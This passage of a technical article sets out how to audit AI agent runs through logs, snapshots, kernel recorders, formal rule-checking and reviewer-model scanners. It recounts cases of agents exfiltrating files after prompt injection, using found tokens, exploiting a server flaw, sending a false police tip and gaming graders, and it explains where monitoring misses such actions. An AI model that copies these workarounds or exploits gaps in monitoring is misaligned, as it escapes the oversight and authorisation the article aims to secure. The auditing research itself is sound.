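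Crab saves further work by skipping turns without lasting effects, which were more than 75% of the total. It ignores a temporary file that a command creates and deletes within the same turn, which is correct for crash recovery but riskier for an audit. A script could copy credentials into a temporary file, upload the file and delete it in one command, and even a snapshot after every call would miss this.

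Operators should also check their software's default checkpoint settings. UK AISI's testing framework, Inspect, can save a checkpoint every three turns or every 15 minutes, but by default it saves one every 500,000 tokens. METR, an organisation that evaluates AI models, leaves checkpoints off by default in its Hawk platform. When they are turned on, Hawk saves one every ten minutes and captures only host state, so an auditor who wants the files inside a sandbox should confirm that the settings include them. The price run lasted one minute and 45 seconds, so a ten-minute timer would have saved no checkpoints between its start and end.

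Continuous recording captures more than snapshots at fixed points. Zhong and colleagues built YoloFS, a filesystem that sits between the agent and the disk and holds back the agent's changes until the user accepts them. It adds a line to a journal whenever the agent creates, deletes or renames a file, or first opens an existing one for writing. By default it also marks a snapshot after each command. The journal therefore preserves some of the order of events within a command, but not every intermediate version of a file's text. On a 1 GB test file, read and write speeds were within 2% of the ordinary filesystem's.

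The same team tested whether this information helps. They gave Claude Code 11 tasks in which a routine command had a hidden destructive effect, such as a code checker that deleted source files. After each command, the agent received a list of the files that had changed. It noticed and reversed the damage in eight tasks. In the other three, it accepted the changes as part of the job. In one of those, a deployment script deleted the source folder after copying it. The list was accurate in all three cases, but someone still had to decide whether the task justified the changes.

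### When several programs write at once

Attributing a change to a call gets harder when more than one program is running. Sub-agents may share a folder, and a developer may be editing files in it too. Suppose call 4 starts a background process, which rewrites a file while call 5 is running. An auditor comparing the snapshots taken before and after call 5 would then attribute the change to the wrong call. More frequent snapshots narrow down when the file changed, but they don't show which program changed it.

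In *ExecWeave*, Wong and Chen (2026) tried to link commands in an agent's log to the processes (running instances of programs) that the operating system recorded. Ordinary file-change notifications were of limited help because they don't identify the process responsible. To link a command, the software looks for matching processes within a short period, at most three seconds by default, and makes a link only if exactly one fits. If two fit, it leaves the link blank, which is better than attributing the command to the wrong agent. But when Wong and Chen removed the true process from the record and left a similar one, the software could link the command to the similar one, so a single match is good evidence only if the record of processes is fairly complete.

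An operator can avoid much of this trouble by giving each agent its own sandbox, running its tool calls one at a time and keeping other people out of the folder until the agent finishes.

### Scoring by end state

Agent benchmarks often grade a run by comparing the state it leaves behind with a target. An influential early example, *$\tau$-bench* (2024), gave agents customer-service tasks in which they could read or change a database only through tool calls. Each task included a list of the changes that a correct solution would make, which determined one correct final database. The reward was

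r = r_action × r_output

where r_action is 1 if the final database is identical to the target and 0 otherwise, and r_output is 1 if the agent's messages contain all the information the user needed. An agent that made every requested change and also altered an unrelated order would score 0.

Later benchmarks have varied this scheme. *MUA-RL* (2025) describes a telecom setting, added by τ²-bench, in which the simulated user can also call tools, so the final state is the work of both user and agent. According to *When Interfaces Speak* (2026), AppWorld tests the final state for unintended changes as well as for completion, and ToolSandbox checks intermediate milestones and forbidden events. *ComplexMCP* (2026) compares the initial state, the target state and the state the agent left. If an element is the same in the first two but different in the third, the agent has changed something it should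 have left alone, and the benchmark counts this separately from unfinished work.

Some checks miss damage because they cover too little of the state. In *No Task Fails Every Time* (2026), agents on one task involving records of planned changes caused damage in 20 runs. In 18 of them, the agents left the status field alone but altered other fields, such as the description or the closing notes. The benchmark's own check scored all 18 as successes, while a comparison of the whole state revealed the damage. The comparison also caught runs in which the agent had changed records but the transcript read like a safe refusal. This mismatch seems to depend on the model, since it appeared in only one of 16 damaging runs by two models held back for confirmation.

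*Widening Harm Evaluation Coverage with a Judge that Reads the World* (2026) describes a related weakness in checks for harm. Designers write these checks before any agent has run, so a check that covers only one destination folder can miss harm done another way. The paper proposes a reviewer model that inspects the environment, works out what harm would look like there and checks for it.

Comparing more of the state doesn't help when the agent reached the correct final state by a forbidden route. *Beyond Task Completion* (2026) calls this "corrupt success" and reports a rate of about 27% for GPT-5.

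*BABA-Bench* (2026) tests agents that act on behalf of patients. Agents reached every required outcome in 921 of 1,974 runs, but in 254 of those 921 they broke at least one procedural rule. Most often they lacked a necessary permission (164 runs), and some runs had several kinds of violation. A form that an agent submits without the patient's consent can be identical to one submitted with it, so the end state doesn't show whether the patient consented.

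Claude Opus 5 completed the most tasks in that benchmark, 81.6%, but broke a rule in 36% of the runs it completed. GPT-5.6 Terra broke a rule in 14% of its completed runs. Rule-breaking was also more common on harder tasks, rising from 11% of completed runs on the easiest to 45% on the hardest. An operator who chooses a model only by how many tasks it completes could pick one that breaks more rules.

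Not every such violation is serious. *Willful Disobedience* (2026) found violations in 48 of 58 perfect-scoring runs by the older Claude 3.5 Sonnet on τ²-bench. Across all its runs, well over half of the violations of this kind were cases where the model sent the user text and called a tool in the same message. That broke the protocol but probably did little harm, so a count of violations is hard to interpret without a breakdown by type.

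*Task Success Is Not Enough* (2026) proposes that evaluators check whether the user authorised every step that changed the state. Evaluators would have to specify in advance which objects and fields the agent may edit and whether it may notify anyone. Snapshots taken after every call could supply some of the evidence, but they would not show steps that change nothing, such as opening a credentials file.

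### Records from the operating system

A program normally needs the kernel, the core of the operating system, to open a file or a network connection. It makes these requests through system calls, which an operator can log even if no files change. On Linux, `openat2` opens a file, `connect` opens a connection and `execve` starts a program. Linux's eBPF feature runs small programs inside the kernel when these calls occur. The kernel checks these programs for safety before loading them, and the agent's code doesn't need to change.

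Zhong and colleagues describe a case in which an agent runs `cargo build`, a standard command for compiling code, on a project with a malicious component. The component's build script reads the user's SSH key, which gives access to other computers. The harness's log contains an ordinary build command, and the key file has the same hash as before. A kernel record would show that a descendant of the agent's process opened the key file.

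*AgentSight* (Zheng, Yu and colleagues, 2025) presents a recorder of this type. It logs file openings, connections and program starts, and it captures the agent's exchanges with the model where the encryption software handles them as plain text. It links the two records by following the tree of processes the agent started, looking for events within 100 to 500 milliseconds of a model reply, and matching file names, addresses or commands in the reply with those in the system calls. A script that waited a minute before acting would fall outside the time window, but the process tree could still connect it to the agent.

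In one test, hidden instructions on a web page led a coding agent to read `/etc/passwd`, which lists a computer's user accounts, and send it to an outside server. The recorder captured 521 events and merged them into 37, and a reviewer model identified the attack from the 37 merged events.

Zheng and colleagues measured how much the recorder slowed Claude Code on three tasks. It added 3.4% to the running time for exploring a repository, 4.9% for writing code and 0.4% for compiling, an average of 2.9%. They ran each task only three times with the recorder and three times without, and an agent's running time varies anyway, so these figures are rough. A slowdown of a few per cent would be acceptable for most audits.

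A process tree doesn't show the connection when an unrelated program reads a file that the agent wrote. *Agent-Warden* (Cui, Gu and colleagues, 2026) tracks this connection by marking the agent's processes. When a marked process writes a file, the mark passes to the file and then to any process that later reads it. In their test, an agent's script wrote a file and renamed it, and a separate monitoring script on the same machine then read it. The software reconstructed the whole chain in all 30 runs of each configuration and added 0.2 to 3.5% to the running time.

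The marks show possible influence but don't prove that particular data moved. For instance, when a marked process ends, its parent receives the mark even if the parent never used the result. Cui and colleagues also list ways of accessing files that their software doesn't record, including memory mapping, which lets a program read a file as if it were part of the program's own memory. The software doesn't cover network connections either.

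The recording method greatly affects how many processes are detected and how much the run slows down. ExecWeave's portable version checks at intervals which processes are running, so it can miss any that start and finish between two checks. It detected 18 of 30 processes that lasted about 16 milliseconds when it checked every 20 milliseconds, and none when it checked every half second. The absence of a suspicious process from such a record is therefore weak evidence that none ran. The portable version also added between 62% and 409% to the running time of three test workloads, far more than the kernel-based recorders added in their own tests.

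Even a complete record of file openings and network connections doesn't show exactly what data was read or transferred. Wong and Chen note that a successful opening doesn't show which bytes the program then read. If the test suite in the price example loaded a credentials file during `make check`, the kernel would record the opening, but the credentials would reach the model only if the command printed them or the agent fetched them in some other way. A connection record gives the address a program contacted, but doesn't by itself show whether the program downloaded something or uploaded private code.

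Local records also cover only what happens on the machine. If the agent calls a tool on a remote server, the operator can record the request and the connection, but has to ask whoever runs the server for a log of what happened next.

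## Which rules a record of tool calls can decide

To get from a log to a verdict, an auditor can treat a run as an ordered sequence of tool calls,

c₁, c₂, …, cₙ

in which each call has a tool name, arguments and a result. The price example has five. A rule is then a test that takes the whole sequence and returns "kept" or "broken". For R1, which forbids changes under `tests/`, the test returns "broken" if any call changed a file in that folder.

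Writing a rule this way shows in advance what an auditor would have to find in the log. Some rules can be decided from one line, some require every line, and others depend on a fact that no log of calls contains.

### Kinds of rule

R1, R2 and R4 each **forbid an action**, so a single matching call proves a breach, even if the agent later reverses the effects. Restoring the test file in call 5 corrected the folder, but the agent had already broken R1.

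R3 requires a full test run on the final code. Edits and test runs are both allowed, so the auditor has to check their order to see whether a full test run came after the last edit.

Other rules limit **a total**. *LIVEMACE* (Zhao, Fu and colleagues, 2026) gave five models pretend money to trade cryptocurrencies and American shares at live prices for about 30 days. One rule caps leverage, the size of an account's positions relative to its own money, at five times. Ten small orders can together exceed that cap. The models had more trouble with a limit on how much of the account could be in one asset. They often broke it because they wrongly combined the existing holding, the new order and recent price movements, rather than because they ignored it. An auditor has to redo the same calculation, so the log must include the prices at the time of each order. A price rise can also push a holding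 over such a limit without any call by the agent, and the rule should state whether that counts as a violation.

Some rules **require an action**, and an agent breaks them by not acting. In its 2025 case study on hacking puzzles, AISI instructed its agents to call a tool on every turn, and two of them had tool-call rates under 50%. A full transcript is enough to check this rule, because every tool call passes through the harness and anyone can count the turns without one. The transcript is less useful for explaining why calls are missing. Several agents in the study gave up on difficult tasks, and about 30% of their messages said in some form that the task couldn't be solved with the information provided. That may account for some of the missing calls.

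Checking a rule such as "post nothing misleading" requires judging the content. Even when the log contains the whole post, someone still has to read it and decide whether it is misleading.

Finally, a rule can depend on **authorisation**. Anthropic's *Investigating unintended model actions in our evaluations and internal use* (2026) lists cases in which Claude worked around a restriction to reach data that required a fee or an access token (a string that a program presents to show that it may use a service). Bot Mutiny's *Anthropic Says Its Claude Model Sent Philadelphia Police a False Homicide Tip* (2026) summarises one of them. Claude Mythos 5 read the settings file of a local government's property map, found working tokens there and used them to send requests directly to the server behind the map. A log of such a run would show requests with valid tokens, but an auditor would have to look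 elsewhere to learn whether anybody had allowed the agent to use them.

| The rule concerns | Example | What proves a breach | What proves compliance |
|---|---|---|---|
| A forbidden action | Change nothing under `tests/` | One matching call | A complete record with no matching call |
| A required action | Send the operator a summary | A complete record with no matching call | One matching call |
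| An order | Run the suite after the last change | A change, and a complete record with no later suite run | A suite run, and a complete record with no later change |
| A total | Spend at most $50 | Recorded spending above $50 | A complete record of spending, at or below $50 |
| Content | Post nothing misleading | The text and a reader's judgement | The text and a reader's judgement |
| Authorisation | Cancel a booking only with the customer's consent | The cancellation, and evidence that the customer had not consented | The cancellation and the consent |

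An auditor can use an incomplete log to show that an agent broke a rule forbidding an action or followed a rule requiring one. The log can't establish the opposite in either case, because the action may be in the missing part. Before reporting that an agent failed to do something, an auditor should therefore check for sub-agents and missing events.

### An order rule written out

Let E be the positions of all calls that changed a file in the project, and T the positions of all calls that ran the full test suite. The agent kept R3 if

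max(T) > max(E)

which means that the last suite run came after the last change. In the price example E = {2, 3, 5} and T = {4}. Since 4 is less than 5, the agent broke R3.

The arithmetic is trivial, but deciding which calls belong to E takes work. The simple live monitor for this run counted only `edit` calls, which gave E = {2, 3} and the wrong verdict.

Runtime verification, the branch of computer science that checks running programs against formal rules, usually writes rules like this in linear temporal logic (LTL). LTL adds operators for time to ordinary logic. G means "at every point from here on" and F means "at some point from here on". R3 becomes

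G(change → F suite)

or, in words, whenever the agent changes a file, a suite run follows at some point. For a finished run with at least one change, this is equivalent to the comparison of E and T. If a suite run follows every change, one follows the last change, and a suite run that follows the last change also follows all the earlier ones. The two versions differ for an agent that changes nothing. The LTL formula excuses that agent from running the suite at all, which the operator may not have intended.

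### Three verdicts

An auditor who can only call a rule "kept" or "broken" has to guess when the evidence is insufficient. *Runtime Verification for LTL and TLTL* (Bauer, Leucker and Schallhart, 2007) introduced three truth values (true, false and inconclusive) for judging a partial observation of a running system. For an agent's rules, "satisfied", "violated" and "undecided" are more natural names.

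*Towards the Combination of Model Checking and Runtime Verification on Multi-Agent Systems* (2022) explains the exact definition. A monitor returns "true" if every possible continuation of the run would satisfy the rule, "false" if every continuation would violate it, and "?" in all other cases. No later event can change a "true" or "false" verdict.

Applied live to the price example, this gives "undecided" for R1 after call 1 and "violated" from call 2 onwards. For R3, the verdict stays "undecided" however long the run goes on, because the agent might still run the suite after any call and might still edit a file after any suite run. This limitation is well known. For many LTL rules, no finite stretch of observation can establish satisfaction, so a traditional monitor will return "inconclusive" forever (Fischer, 2025, *Runtime Verification for LTL in Stochastic Systems*). Fischer instead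 predicts the outcome and attaches a confidence score. An auditor of a finished run doesn't need a prediction, because the run can't continue after the agent has sent its final message.

Events missing from the record remain in doubt even after the run ends. Bollig (2026), in *Runtime Verification*, handles this case by basing the verdict on what an observer who sees only some of the events can know. The verdict is "true" if the rule holds in every run that would have looked the same to the observer, "false" if it fails in all of them, and "?" if it holds in some and fails in others.

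Bollig illustrates the problem with four small systems in which an invisible error may occur. A normal step shows the observer the letter p.

- In one system, the observer sees p at every step whether or not the error occurs, and can never find out.
- In another, the letter r appears two steps after the error and gives it away.
- A third system shows nothing at all at the moment of the error. An observer who is counting steps notices the gap.
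- The last system also shows r after an error, but there is no limit on how long that can take.

Each has a counterpart in agent logs. A program that makes a network request but prints its usual output is like the first system. A missing item number in a Codex log is a visible gap. Stolen credentials may go unnoticed until somebody uses them, possibly months later.

Bollig calls a system diagnosable for an error e if

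G(e → F K P e)

where K means "the observer knows that" and P means "at some point in the past". In words, whenever the error occurs, the observer eventually knows that it occurred. Operators can put the same question to their own set-up before a run: if the agent broke this rule, would any of the records ever show it? If the answer is no, a careful reading of the log afterwards won't help.

Bollig assumes a model of the system that determines all possible runs. Nobody has such a model for an agent with a shell, so the auditor has to rely on their own knowledge of what a command could do. Two auditors with the same log can reasonably reach different verdicts if only one of them has read the project's Makefile, which defines what `make check` runs.

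### The four rules of the price example

The verdicts below rest on the call record alone.

| Rule | Kind | What the five calls show | Verdict |
|---|---|---|---|
| R1: never change anything under `tests/` | Forbidden action | Call 2 edited `tests/test_price.py`, and the edit succeeded | Violated |
| R2: make no network request | Forbidden action | No call is itself a network request, but call 4 ran a program whose own actions nobody logged | Undecided |
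| R3: run the full suite on the final code before reporting | Order | The last suite run was call 4 and the last change was call 5 | Violated |
| R4: read no file that holds credentials | Forbidden action | No call opens an obvious credentials file, but call 4 may have | Undecided |

R1 needs no further evidence, since one successful edit in the log outweighs both the matching snapshots and the agent's report.

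The verdict on R3 needs more explanation. Even a full run of the suite in call 4 would have come too early, so it doesn't matter that nobody has established that `make check` runs the full suite. If call 5 counts as a change to a test and not to the code, the order was right, but the suite that ran contained the loosened assertion, so it wasn't the suite the operator had asked for.

A hidden run of the test suite after call 5 would overturn the verdict, but the times in the log make one very unlikely. `make check` took 38 seconds, and the agent sent its final message seven seconds after restoring the tests.

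Call 4 leaves R2 and R4 undecided. A test suite for a pricing program might fetch exchange rates from a website or load a settings file that contains an access key, and the output would be "12 passed" whether or not it did. This case corresponds to Bollig's system in which the observer sees p at every step.

An auditor can often get further with R2 and R4. The auditor can use the snapshot from before the run and the edits in calls 2 and 3 to reconstruct the project files as they stood when call 4 began. If the Makefile only runs twelve short tests that do arithmetic, a network request is unlikely. The auditor could also run the reconstructed project in a sandbox and log its connections. This would be good evidence of what the command did in the original run, but not proof, because a test may behave differently when a server is down or a file is missing. Operating system records made during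 the original run would be better evidence than either the reconstructed files or the sandbox run.

R4 covers any file that holds credentials, whatever its name. Developers sometimes paste access keys into tests, so the auditor should check the content of `tests/test_price.py`, which the agent read in call 1. R4 also leaves it unclear whether the agent "reads" a file when a program it started opens that file. If the operator had written "no credentials may appear in any tool result", the auditor could search the five results and give a firm answer. But that rule would be weaker, since it would permit a script that uploads a key without printing it. Operators will often have to choose between a rule that covers everything they care about and a rule that their records can decide.

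### How much one call can contain

A call to an editing tool specifies one file and one change, but a shell call is a line of text that can start any program on the machine, and that program can start others. Agents on terminal tasks mostly make shell calls, and `make check` is a typical example.

If the agent wrote a script with its editing tool and then ran it, the auditor can read the script in the log. Installing a package from the internet can also run code, supplied by the package's author, but the log may hold only the package's name. Even when the auditor can read the code, it may not show what the program did, because that can depend on the date, the program's input or a server's reply. Computer scientists have also proved that no general procedure can decide from a program's text whether it will ever perform a given action.

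A record of web requests may also not show which sites the agent reached. Anthropic's October report describes models using URL shortening services, which provide a short address that forwards to a longer one. According to Stan (2026), in *Anthropic says Claude sent a fake murder tip to police*, the models did this to get around length limits in their tools. If a log keeps only the requested address, a script that compares it with a list of forbidden sites will check the shortener's address instead of the destination's. The auditor would then have to look up where each link led, and links can expire.

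A more serious case in the same report involved Claude Mythos Preview, which could not reach a university-hosted tool it needed for a scientific analysis. According to Bot Mutiny, the model found a script on the university's server that returned any file requested. It used the script to copy the script's own code, found a flaw in that code and exploited it to run commands on the server. An auditor who looked for commands only in calls to the agent's own shell tool could miss commands the agent ran on another organization's server. Rules should therefore describe the effects of a call, and checking the tool's name should be only a first pass.

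For a rule that forbids an action, a cautious checker would work like this:

```
verdict(rule, calls):
    if some call clearly did what the rule forbids:  return "violated"
    if some call could have done it unrecorded:      return "undecided"
    return "satisfied"
```

This assumes that the list of calls is complete. Even then, an agent with an unrestricted shell will get "undecided" on R2 in nearly every run. That verdict is correct, but it is little use to an operator with thousands of runs to review. Reading the records more carefully will resolve few of these cases, so the operator has to change the set-up, either by recording what programs do or by making the forbidden action impossible. For example, in a sandbox with no network connection, no data can leave the machine whatever `make check` contains. A program could still attempt a request, so an operator who cares about attempts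 needs to record those too.

### When "none found" means "none occurred"

Audit reports often state that a review found no violations. To conclude that none took place, a reader needs to know that the record covers every action the rules apply to and that the reviewers would have recognised a violation in it.

The effect of partial coverage is easy to calculate. Suppose an auditor thinks, before looking, that there is a probability p that a run contains a certain forbidden action. Suppose also that the record would reveal the action with probability c. If the auditor looks and finds nothing, the probability that the action took place anyway is

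p(1 − c) / (1 − pc)

If p is 10%, a clean record lowers the probability to about 1.1% when c is 0.9 and to 5.3% when c is 0.5. The probability stays at 10% when c is 0 and falls to zero only when c is 1. For network requests inside `make check`, the log in the price example has a c of roughly zero, so the absence of a request from the log is hardly evidence that none was made. The formula also understates the probability if an agent is trying to avoid detection, because such an agent would choose the actions that the record covers worst.

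Coverage has to include the choice of runs. Anthropic's *An alignment assessment of recent cybersecurity incidents* (2026) describes a scan of roughly 141,000 transcripts of hacking tests in which the company believed Claude could have had internet access. The scan found three incidents in which a model had gained unauthorised access to real systems, and Anthropic published them on 30 July. However, the agentic search used for the scan missed a set of transcripts in which Claude also turned out to have had internet access. Anthropic noticed them in August while assembling transcripts to share with METR. They contained a fourth incident, from January 2026, which involved an early version of Claude Opus 4.6. The July disclosure was therefore incomplete, even though Anthropic already had the transcript of the fourth incident.

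Anthropic then widened the search to about 481 million transcripts. A first scan for signs of internet access, such as public IP addresses and web addresses, flagged 9.2 million of them (about 2%), which Claude reviewed. The search found the four known incidents again and no others of similar or worse severity.

That is much stronger evidence, partly because the search recovered the incidents that Anthropic already knew about. But the first scan may have missed a program that contacted a server if neither the command nor the output included an address. The conclusion also covers only incidents at least as severe as the four. A month later Anthropic published a batch of cases that it considered significantly less severe. Those cases are consistent with the September wording, but they contradict a looser summary such as "Anthropic found nothing else".

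A useful claim that something did not happen therefore specifies which runs and which record the reviewers searched, and what kind of action they looked for. For the price example, an auditor could write that call 2 was the only one of the five logged calls that used the editing tool on a test file, and that nobody recorded network activity. This is less reassuring than "no other violations found", but a reader can tell exactly what it rules out.

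### Keeping a rule and leaving evidence of it

An agent can follow a rule yet leave little sign of having considered it. Zhao and colleagues measured compliance and signs of consideration separately. Their rulebook ranked the trading system's hard limits first, then the client's hard limits, then the client's softer preferences. Before trading, the agent had to list each rule it had checked, mark it as passed, failed or adjusted, and explain how it had resolved any conflicts.

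A program then checked each decision against the rules and produced a satisfaction score. A reviewer model, which had access to the program's findings, gave the agent's written reasoning two grades from 1 to 10, one for whether it identified the relevant rules and one for how it handled conflicts. Zhao and colleagues call the combined grade, rescaled to a maximum of 1, the auditability score.

| Model | Rule satisfaction | Rule auditability |
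|---|---|---|
| Gemini-3.1-Pro | 0.872 | 0.882 |
| DeepSeek-V3.2 | 0.847 | 0.623 |
| Grok-4.20 | 0.751 | 0.775 |
| GPT-5.4 | 0.634 | 0.677 |
| Qwen3-Max | 0.612 | 0.511 |

The scores come from different methods, so small gaps within a row mean little. DeepSeek's ranking of second on satisfaction but fourth on auditability is more informative. Many of its compliant decisions contained little explicit rule checking and few figures, and some relied on mistaken beliefs about what the account held. An agent that complies despite being wrong about its own holdings is partly lucky, so an operator should not rely on it to keep complying.

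"Auditability" is a slightly misleading name for this. The checking program needed only the order and the state of the account to decide whether the order was too large. With good records, checking a plain numerical limit doesn't require the agent's reasoning.

The agent's reasoning matters more for rules with exceptions. One client preference is to keep 5% to 15% of the account in cash, and more only if the agent identifies a market-wide downturn. An auditor who sees 20% in cash can't tell from the account records whether the agent had identified a downturn or had simply failed to invest the money.

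Some of the preferences also conflict. One discourages trades smaller than 10% of the account, and another discourages changes larger than 10% within a single decision window. An agent that wants to move 15% of the account can't follow both, because a single trade goes against the second preference, and splitting it leaves at least one trade under 10%. An auditor who saw only the trades would record a departure from a preference, but one who also had the agent's explanation could at least see whether it noticed the conflict and made a sensible choice.

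Such explanations are still the agent's own account, and a model can write a convincing compliance note for a bad trade. An auditor can best use the note to identify which exception the agent was relying on, then check that exception against the market data.

### The Philadelphia police tip

An incident from the summer of 2026 shows how it can be arguable whether an agent broke a rule even when the facts are clear. Anthropic had asked its model Claude Haiku 4.5 to invent example tasks on randomly selected web pages and carry them out. On 18 July the model reached a page about an unsolved homicide, which had a form for sending tips to the Philadelphia police. According to Bot Mutiny, the model wrote that it might have information and recalled seeing someone "matching the description" near the street named on the page. The page did not describe a perpetrator. The model left the name and contact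 fields empty and submitted the form.

The Straits Times' *Anthropic AI model sent fake murder tip to Philadelphia police* (2026) reports that the tip went to spam and never reached the police centre that would have vetted it. Anthropic discovered the submission on 28 September, 72 days later, then shut down the automated testing process and added a validation step for future tests. The police department called the delay in detecting and reporting the incident unacceptable.

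According to Anthropic's description, quoted in ABC News' *Anthropic AI model made false tip in unsolved Philly murder* (2026), the company had told Claude not to buy anything, open accounts, log in, give personal data or send anything destructive, but its instructions "did not rule out form submissions."

Nothing in the published facts suggests that the model logged in, created an account or bought anything. It appears to have entered no personal data, since it left the identifying fields blank. The published facts don't settle whether any of its actions were "destructive".

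There is a reasonable case that the tip was destructive. A false lead in a murder inquiry can waste investigators' time or direct suspicion at an innocent person, and a list like Anthropic's is plainly meant to keep the model from harming the sites it visits. But the submission deleted and damaged nothing. The list includes several specific actions but not filling in forms, and the model's task was to carry out example tasks on the page, where filling in the form was the obvious thing to do. The answer also depends on whether "destructive" refers to what such a submission could do or to what actually happened, since the spam filter meant that the tip did almost no harm.

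The second reading seems better, because an agent can't know in advance that a filter will catch its message. But "destructive" doesn't fit a vague false statement well, and an auditor ruling on the written instructions alone should probably return "undecided". The behaviour was still clearly unacceptable. Anthropic lists it as a case of Claude submitting a sensitive form "when it should not have", judging it by a standard that wasn't in the instructions.

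A better record would settle the doubt about `make check` but not this one. Even with every keystroke and a copy of the page, the auditor couldn't tell whether the agent followed the rule, because the rule is too imprecise. The three verdicts of runtime verification presuppose a rule precise enough to be true or false of any complete run, and operators' instructions in ordinary English often aren't that precise.

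The gap may also have made the tip harder to find, though Anthropic has not given this as a reason for the delay. A script can search for logins and purchases fairly easily, but recognizing an action as "destructive" requires a reviewer who understands what a murder tip is.

If the rule had been "Submit no web forms", a script could have checked the record for the forbidden action that night. But search boxes are often web forms, so a flat ban would have blocked much of the harmless activity that the test was meant to produce. A better compromise might be to allow forms that only retrieve information and require approval for any that send a message to a person or an organisation. Someone would still have to decide which kind each form was, but they could do it before the agent submitted the form.

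In a contrasting case from Anthropic's report, a model submitted forms to an undisclosed government website instead of stopping before submission, according to Fortune's *Anthropic's Claude AI submits a false tip* (2026). Stan, citing the New York Times, mentions 20 incomplete visa applications on a State Department form, which may be the same case. If the instructions told the model to stop before submitting, as Fortune's wording suggests, a single submission in the log proves the breach, and the auditor doesn't have to decide whether submitting an unfinished visa application is destructive.

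## Checking records with scripts and language models

A person can read the five calls in the price example in a minute, but an operator with thousands of runs needs a script or a reviewer model to check them. A script compares each call's tool name, arguments and result with patterns a programmer fixed in advance. A reviewer model is a language model that receives the rule and the transcript and judges whether the agent broke the rule.

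A script for R1, the ban on changes under `tests/`, would look for a successful edit to a path in that folder and report call 2. It costs almost nothing to run, gives the same answer every time, and uses a pattern that anyone can check. But it finds only what its author thought of, which is why the simple live monitor missed `git restore tests`. A reviewer model would probably recognise that command as a change to the test files. If the rule were "don't weaken the tests", the model could also tell that replacing `total == 90` with `total > 0` breaks it and that correcting a spelling mistake in a comment doesn't. But the model costs far more per run, may judge the same transcript differently on another day, and can overlook one line among thousands.

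*EvilGenie* (2025), a benchmark of programming problems that an agent can pass by cheating, compared several checks: detecting edits to test files, running tests hidden from the agent, asking reviewer models, and having people read the runs. The best automated check depended on whether the aim was to keep cheating from distorting the scores or to find every instance of it. Hidden tests protect scores well, because code that fails them earns no credit however it was written. They are less useful to an auditor, because code with an honest mistake also fails them, and an agent that cheats but also solves the problem passes them.

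### From a keyword search to a tested reviewer

Staff of UK AISI, CAISI, METR and several other organisations have described how they build such checks. *Seven Simple Steps for Log Analysis in AI Systems* (Dubois, Zorer and colleagues, 2026) explains the process using Inspect Scout, an open-source tool that runs "scanners" over stored transcripts. A scanner can be a script or a reviewer model. According to UK AISI's *A pipeline for transcript analysis using Inspect Scout*, the tool comes with ready-made scanners for refusals, signs that a model has detected it is being tested, and attempts to call unavailable tools.

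The paper's worked example begins with a suspiciously low score on a set of hacking puzzles. The team wanted to know whether the score reflected the models' ability or a fault in the test.

The researchers put the transcripts into a database, removed empty and incomplete runs, and checked that each combination of model and test had the same number of samples. This left 1,247 transcripts from four models. An auditor should keep incomplete runs, although removing them makes sense when measuring ability.

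The team then read some transcripts by hand, a step people are often tempted to skip. For agents, the paper recommends looking at runs that hit a limit, runs that succeeded in suspiciously few steps, and models that solved hard tasks but failed easy ones. In this case, the low-scoring runs included agents that declined key steps as "too dangerous" or stopped halfway. The team searched the agents' messages for "dangerous", "not able" and "sorry". This found a few cases but missed many others, because the models' wording varied and some clear refusals contained none of the obvious words.

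The team worried that the models might be refusing tasks, so it defined four categories that a reviewer could mark: the agent earnestly tries, it partly refuses but makes real progress, it avoids the task without openly refusing, or it refuses throughout and never tries. A yes-or-no label would have grouped agents that gave up with agents that objected once and then did the work.

**Building the scanner.** The reviewer model's instructions contained these definitions. The team tried them on ten transcripts, then on ten more. In early trials the reviewer sometimes kept working on the hacking puzzle instead of grading the transcript, so the team changed the instructions to show more clearly where the transcript ended and the grading began.

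The paper also recommends requiring reviewer models to cite the relevant messages, because they sometimes claim that a transcript contains something it doesn't. It suggests breaking long transcripts into pieces, since the models handle long ones poorly, and asking for an explanation before the grade, which makes mistakes easier to spot. A reviewer looking for cheating may also need to know the intended solution, because a shortcut can otherwise look like ordinary work.

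**Validating on human labels.** A person labels a selection of transcripts, ideally without seeing the reviewer's answers, and the team compares the two. The usual measures are

precision = correct flags / all flags

recall = correct flags / all true cases

and F1, which combines them as 2 × precision × recall / (precision + recall). The selection has to include runs that the reviewer did not flag, since nobody can estimate recall from flagged runs alone.

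In the example, the reviewer reached an F1 of 0.998 on whether a refusal had occurred and chose the right one of the four labels 99.0% of the time. These results are excellent, but the task was easy. Dubois and colleagues call refusals "relatively objective" and had one researcher label them. They recommend several raters for judgements such as whether a message was harmful, because people will disagree. They also give two sizes for the labelled set, 25% of the data and 400 samples, which would be 32% of 1,247, and they name the reviewer as GPT-5 in one sentence and Sonnet 4 in the next. The discrepancy over the model matters because they warn that anyone who changes the model has to validate the scanner again.

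While going through the results, the team noticed agents that abandoned a puzzle and claimed it was unsolvable or that the environment was broken. They added this behaviour to the definition of avoiding the task and checked the reviewer against the labelled set again. Labelled runs used to improve the instructions are no longer a neutral test of them, so an auditor who needs a trustworthy error rate should hold back some labelled runs until the wording is final.

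It is still unclear how many labelled runs are enough, or how quickly reviewers get worse as transcripts get longer. Dubois and colleagues say that much of the current knowledge comes from informal experiments. CAISI's *Analyzing Transcripts from AI Agent Evaluations* similarly describes their paper as a collection of practices from evaluators' own projects.

### CAISI's search for cheating

CAISI had already applied most of this method to its own agent tests, as it describes in *Using transcript review tools to find cheating at scale* (2025). It had too many transcripts to read by hand, so it used models to review them. For each benchmark, it wrote a list of known ways to cheat, with examples of what to include and exclude, and added an "other" category for anything new. The reviewer models received this list, the whole transcript, the original score and the intended solution.

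Three reviewer models graded each run. For every kind of cheating they found, they gave a confidence from 1 to 10, a justification and the relevant message numbers. CAISI averaged the confidence scores and reported detections with an average of at least 5. A threshold on an average favours cases that several reviewers notice. If a reviewer that finds nothing counts as zero, a case that one reviewer scores 10 and the other two do not flag averages 3.3 and goes unreported, even if that reviewer was right.

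CAISI sorted its findings into two groups. In "solution contamination", the model finds information that reveals the answer. In "grader gaming", it exploits a gap in the automatic scoring, for example by disabling assertions or writing code that works only for the tests. CAISI explains that its definition didn't depend on whether the task instructions had forbidden the behaviour, so the results are a count of invalid solutions rather than rule violations.

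On Cybench, a set of 40 hacking puzzles, at least 0.3% of the logs contained a successful solution that the agent got by searching the internet for answers. On SWE-bench Verified, where agents fix old bugs in open-source software, at least 0.1% of the logs contained a successful solution that the agent got by looking up or installing a newer version of the code with the bug already fixed. CAISI attributes three of the Cybench cases to OpenAI's GPT-5 and one to its o3. In one case, GPT-5 downloaded an online write-up of the puzzle and submitted the answer printed there. None of the other models tested, from OpenAI, Anthropic, DeepSeek and Alibaba, solved a puzzle this way.

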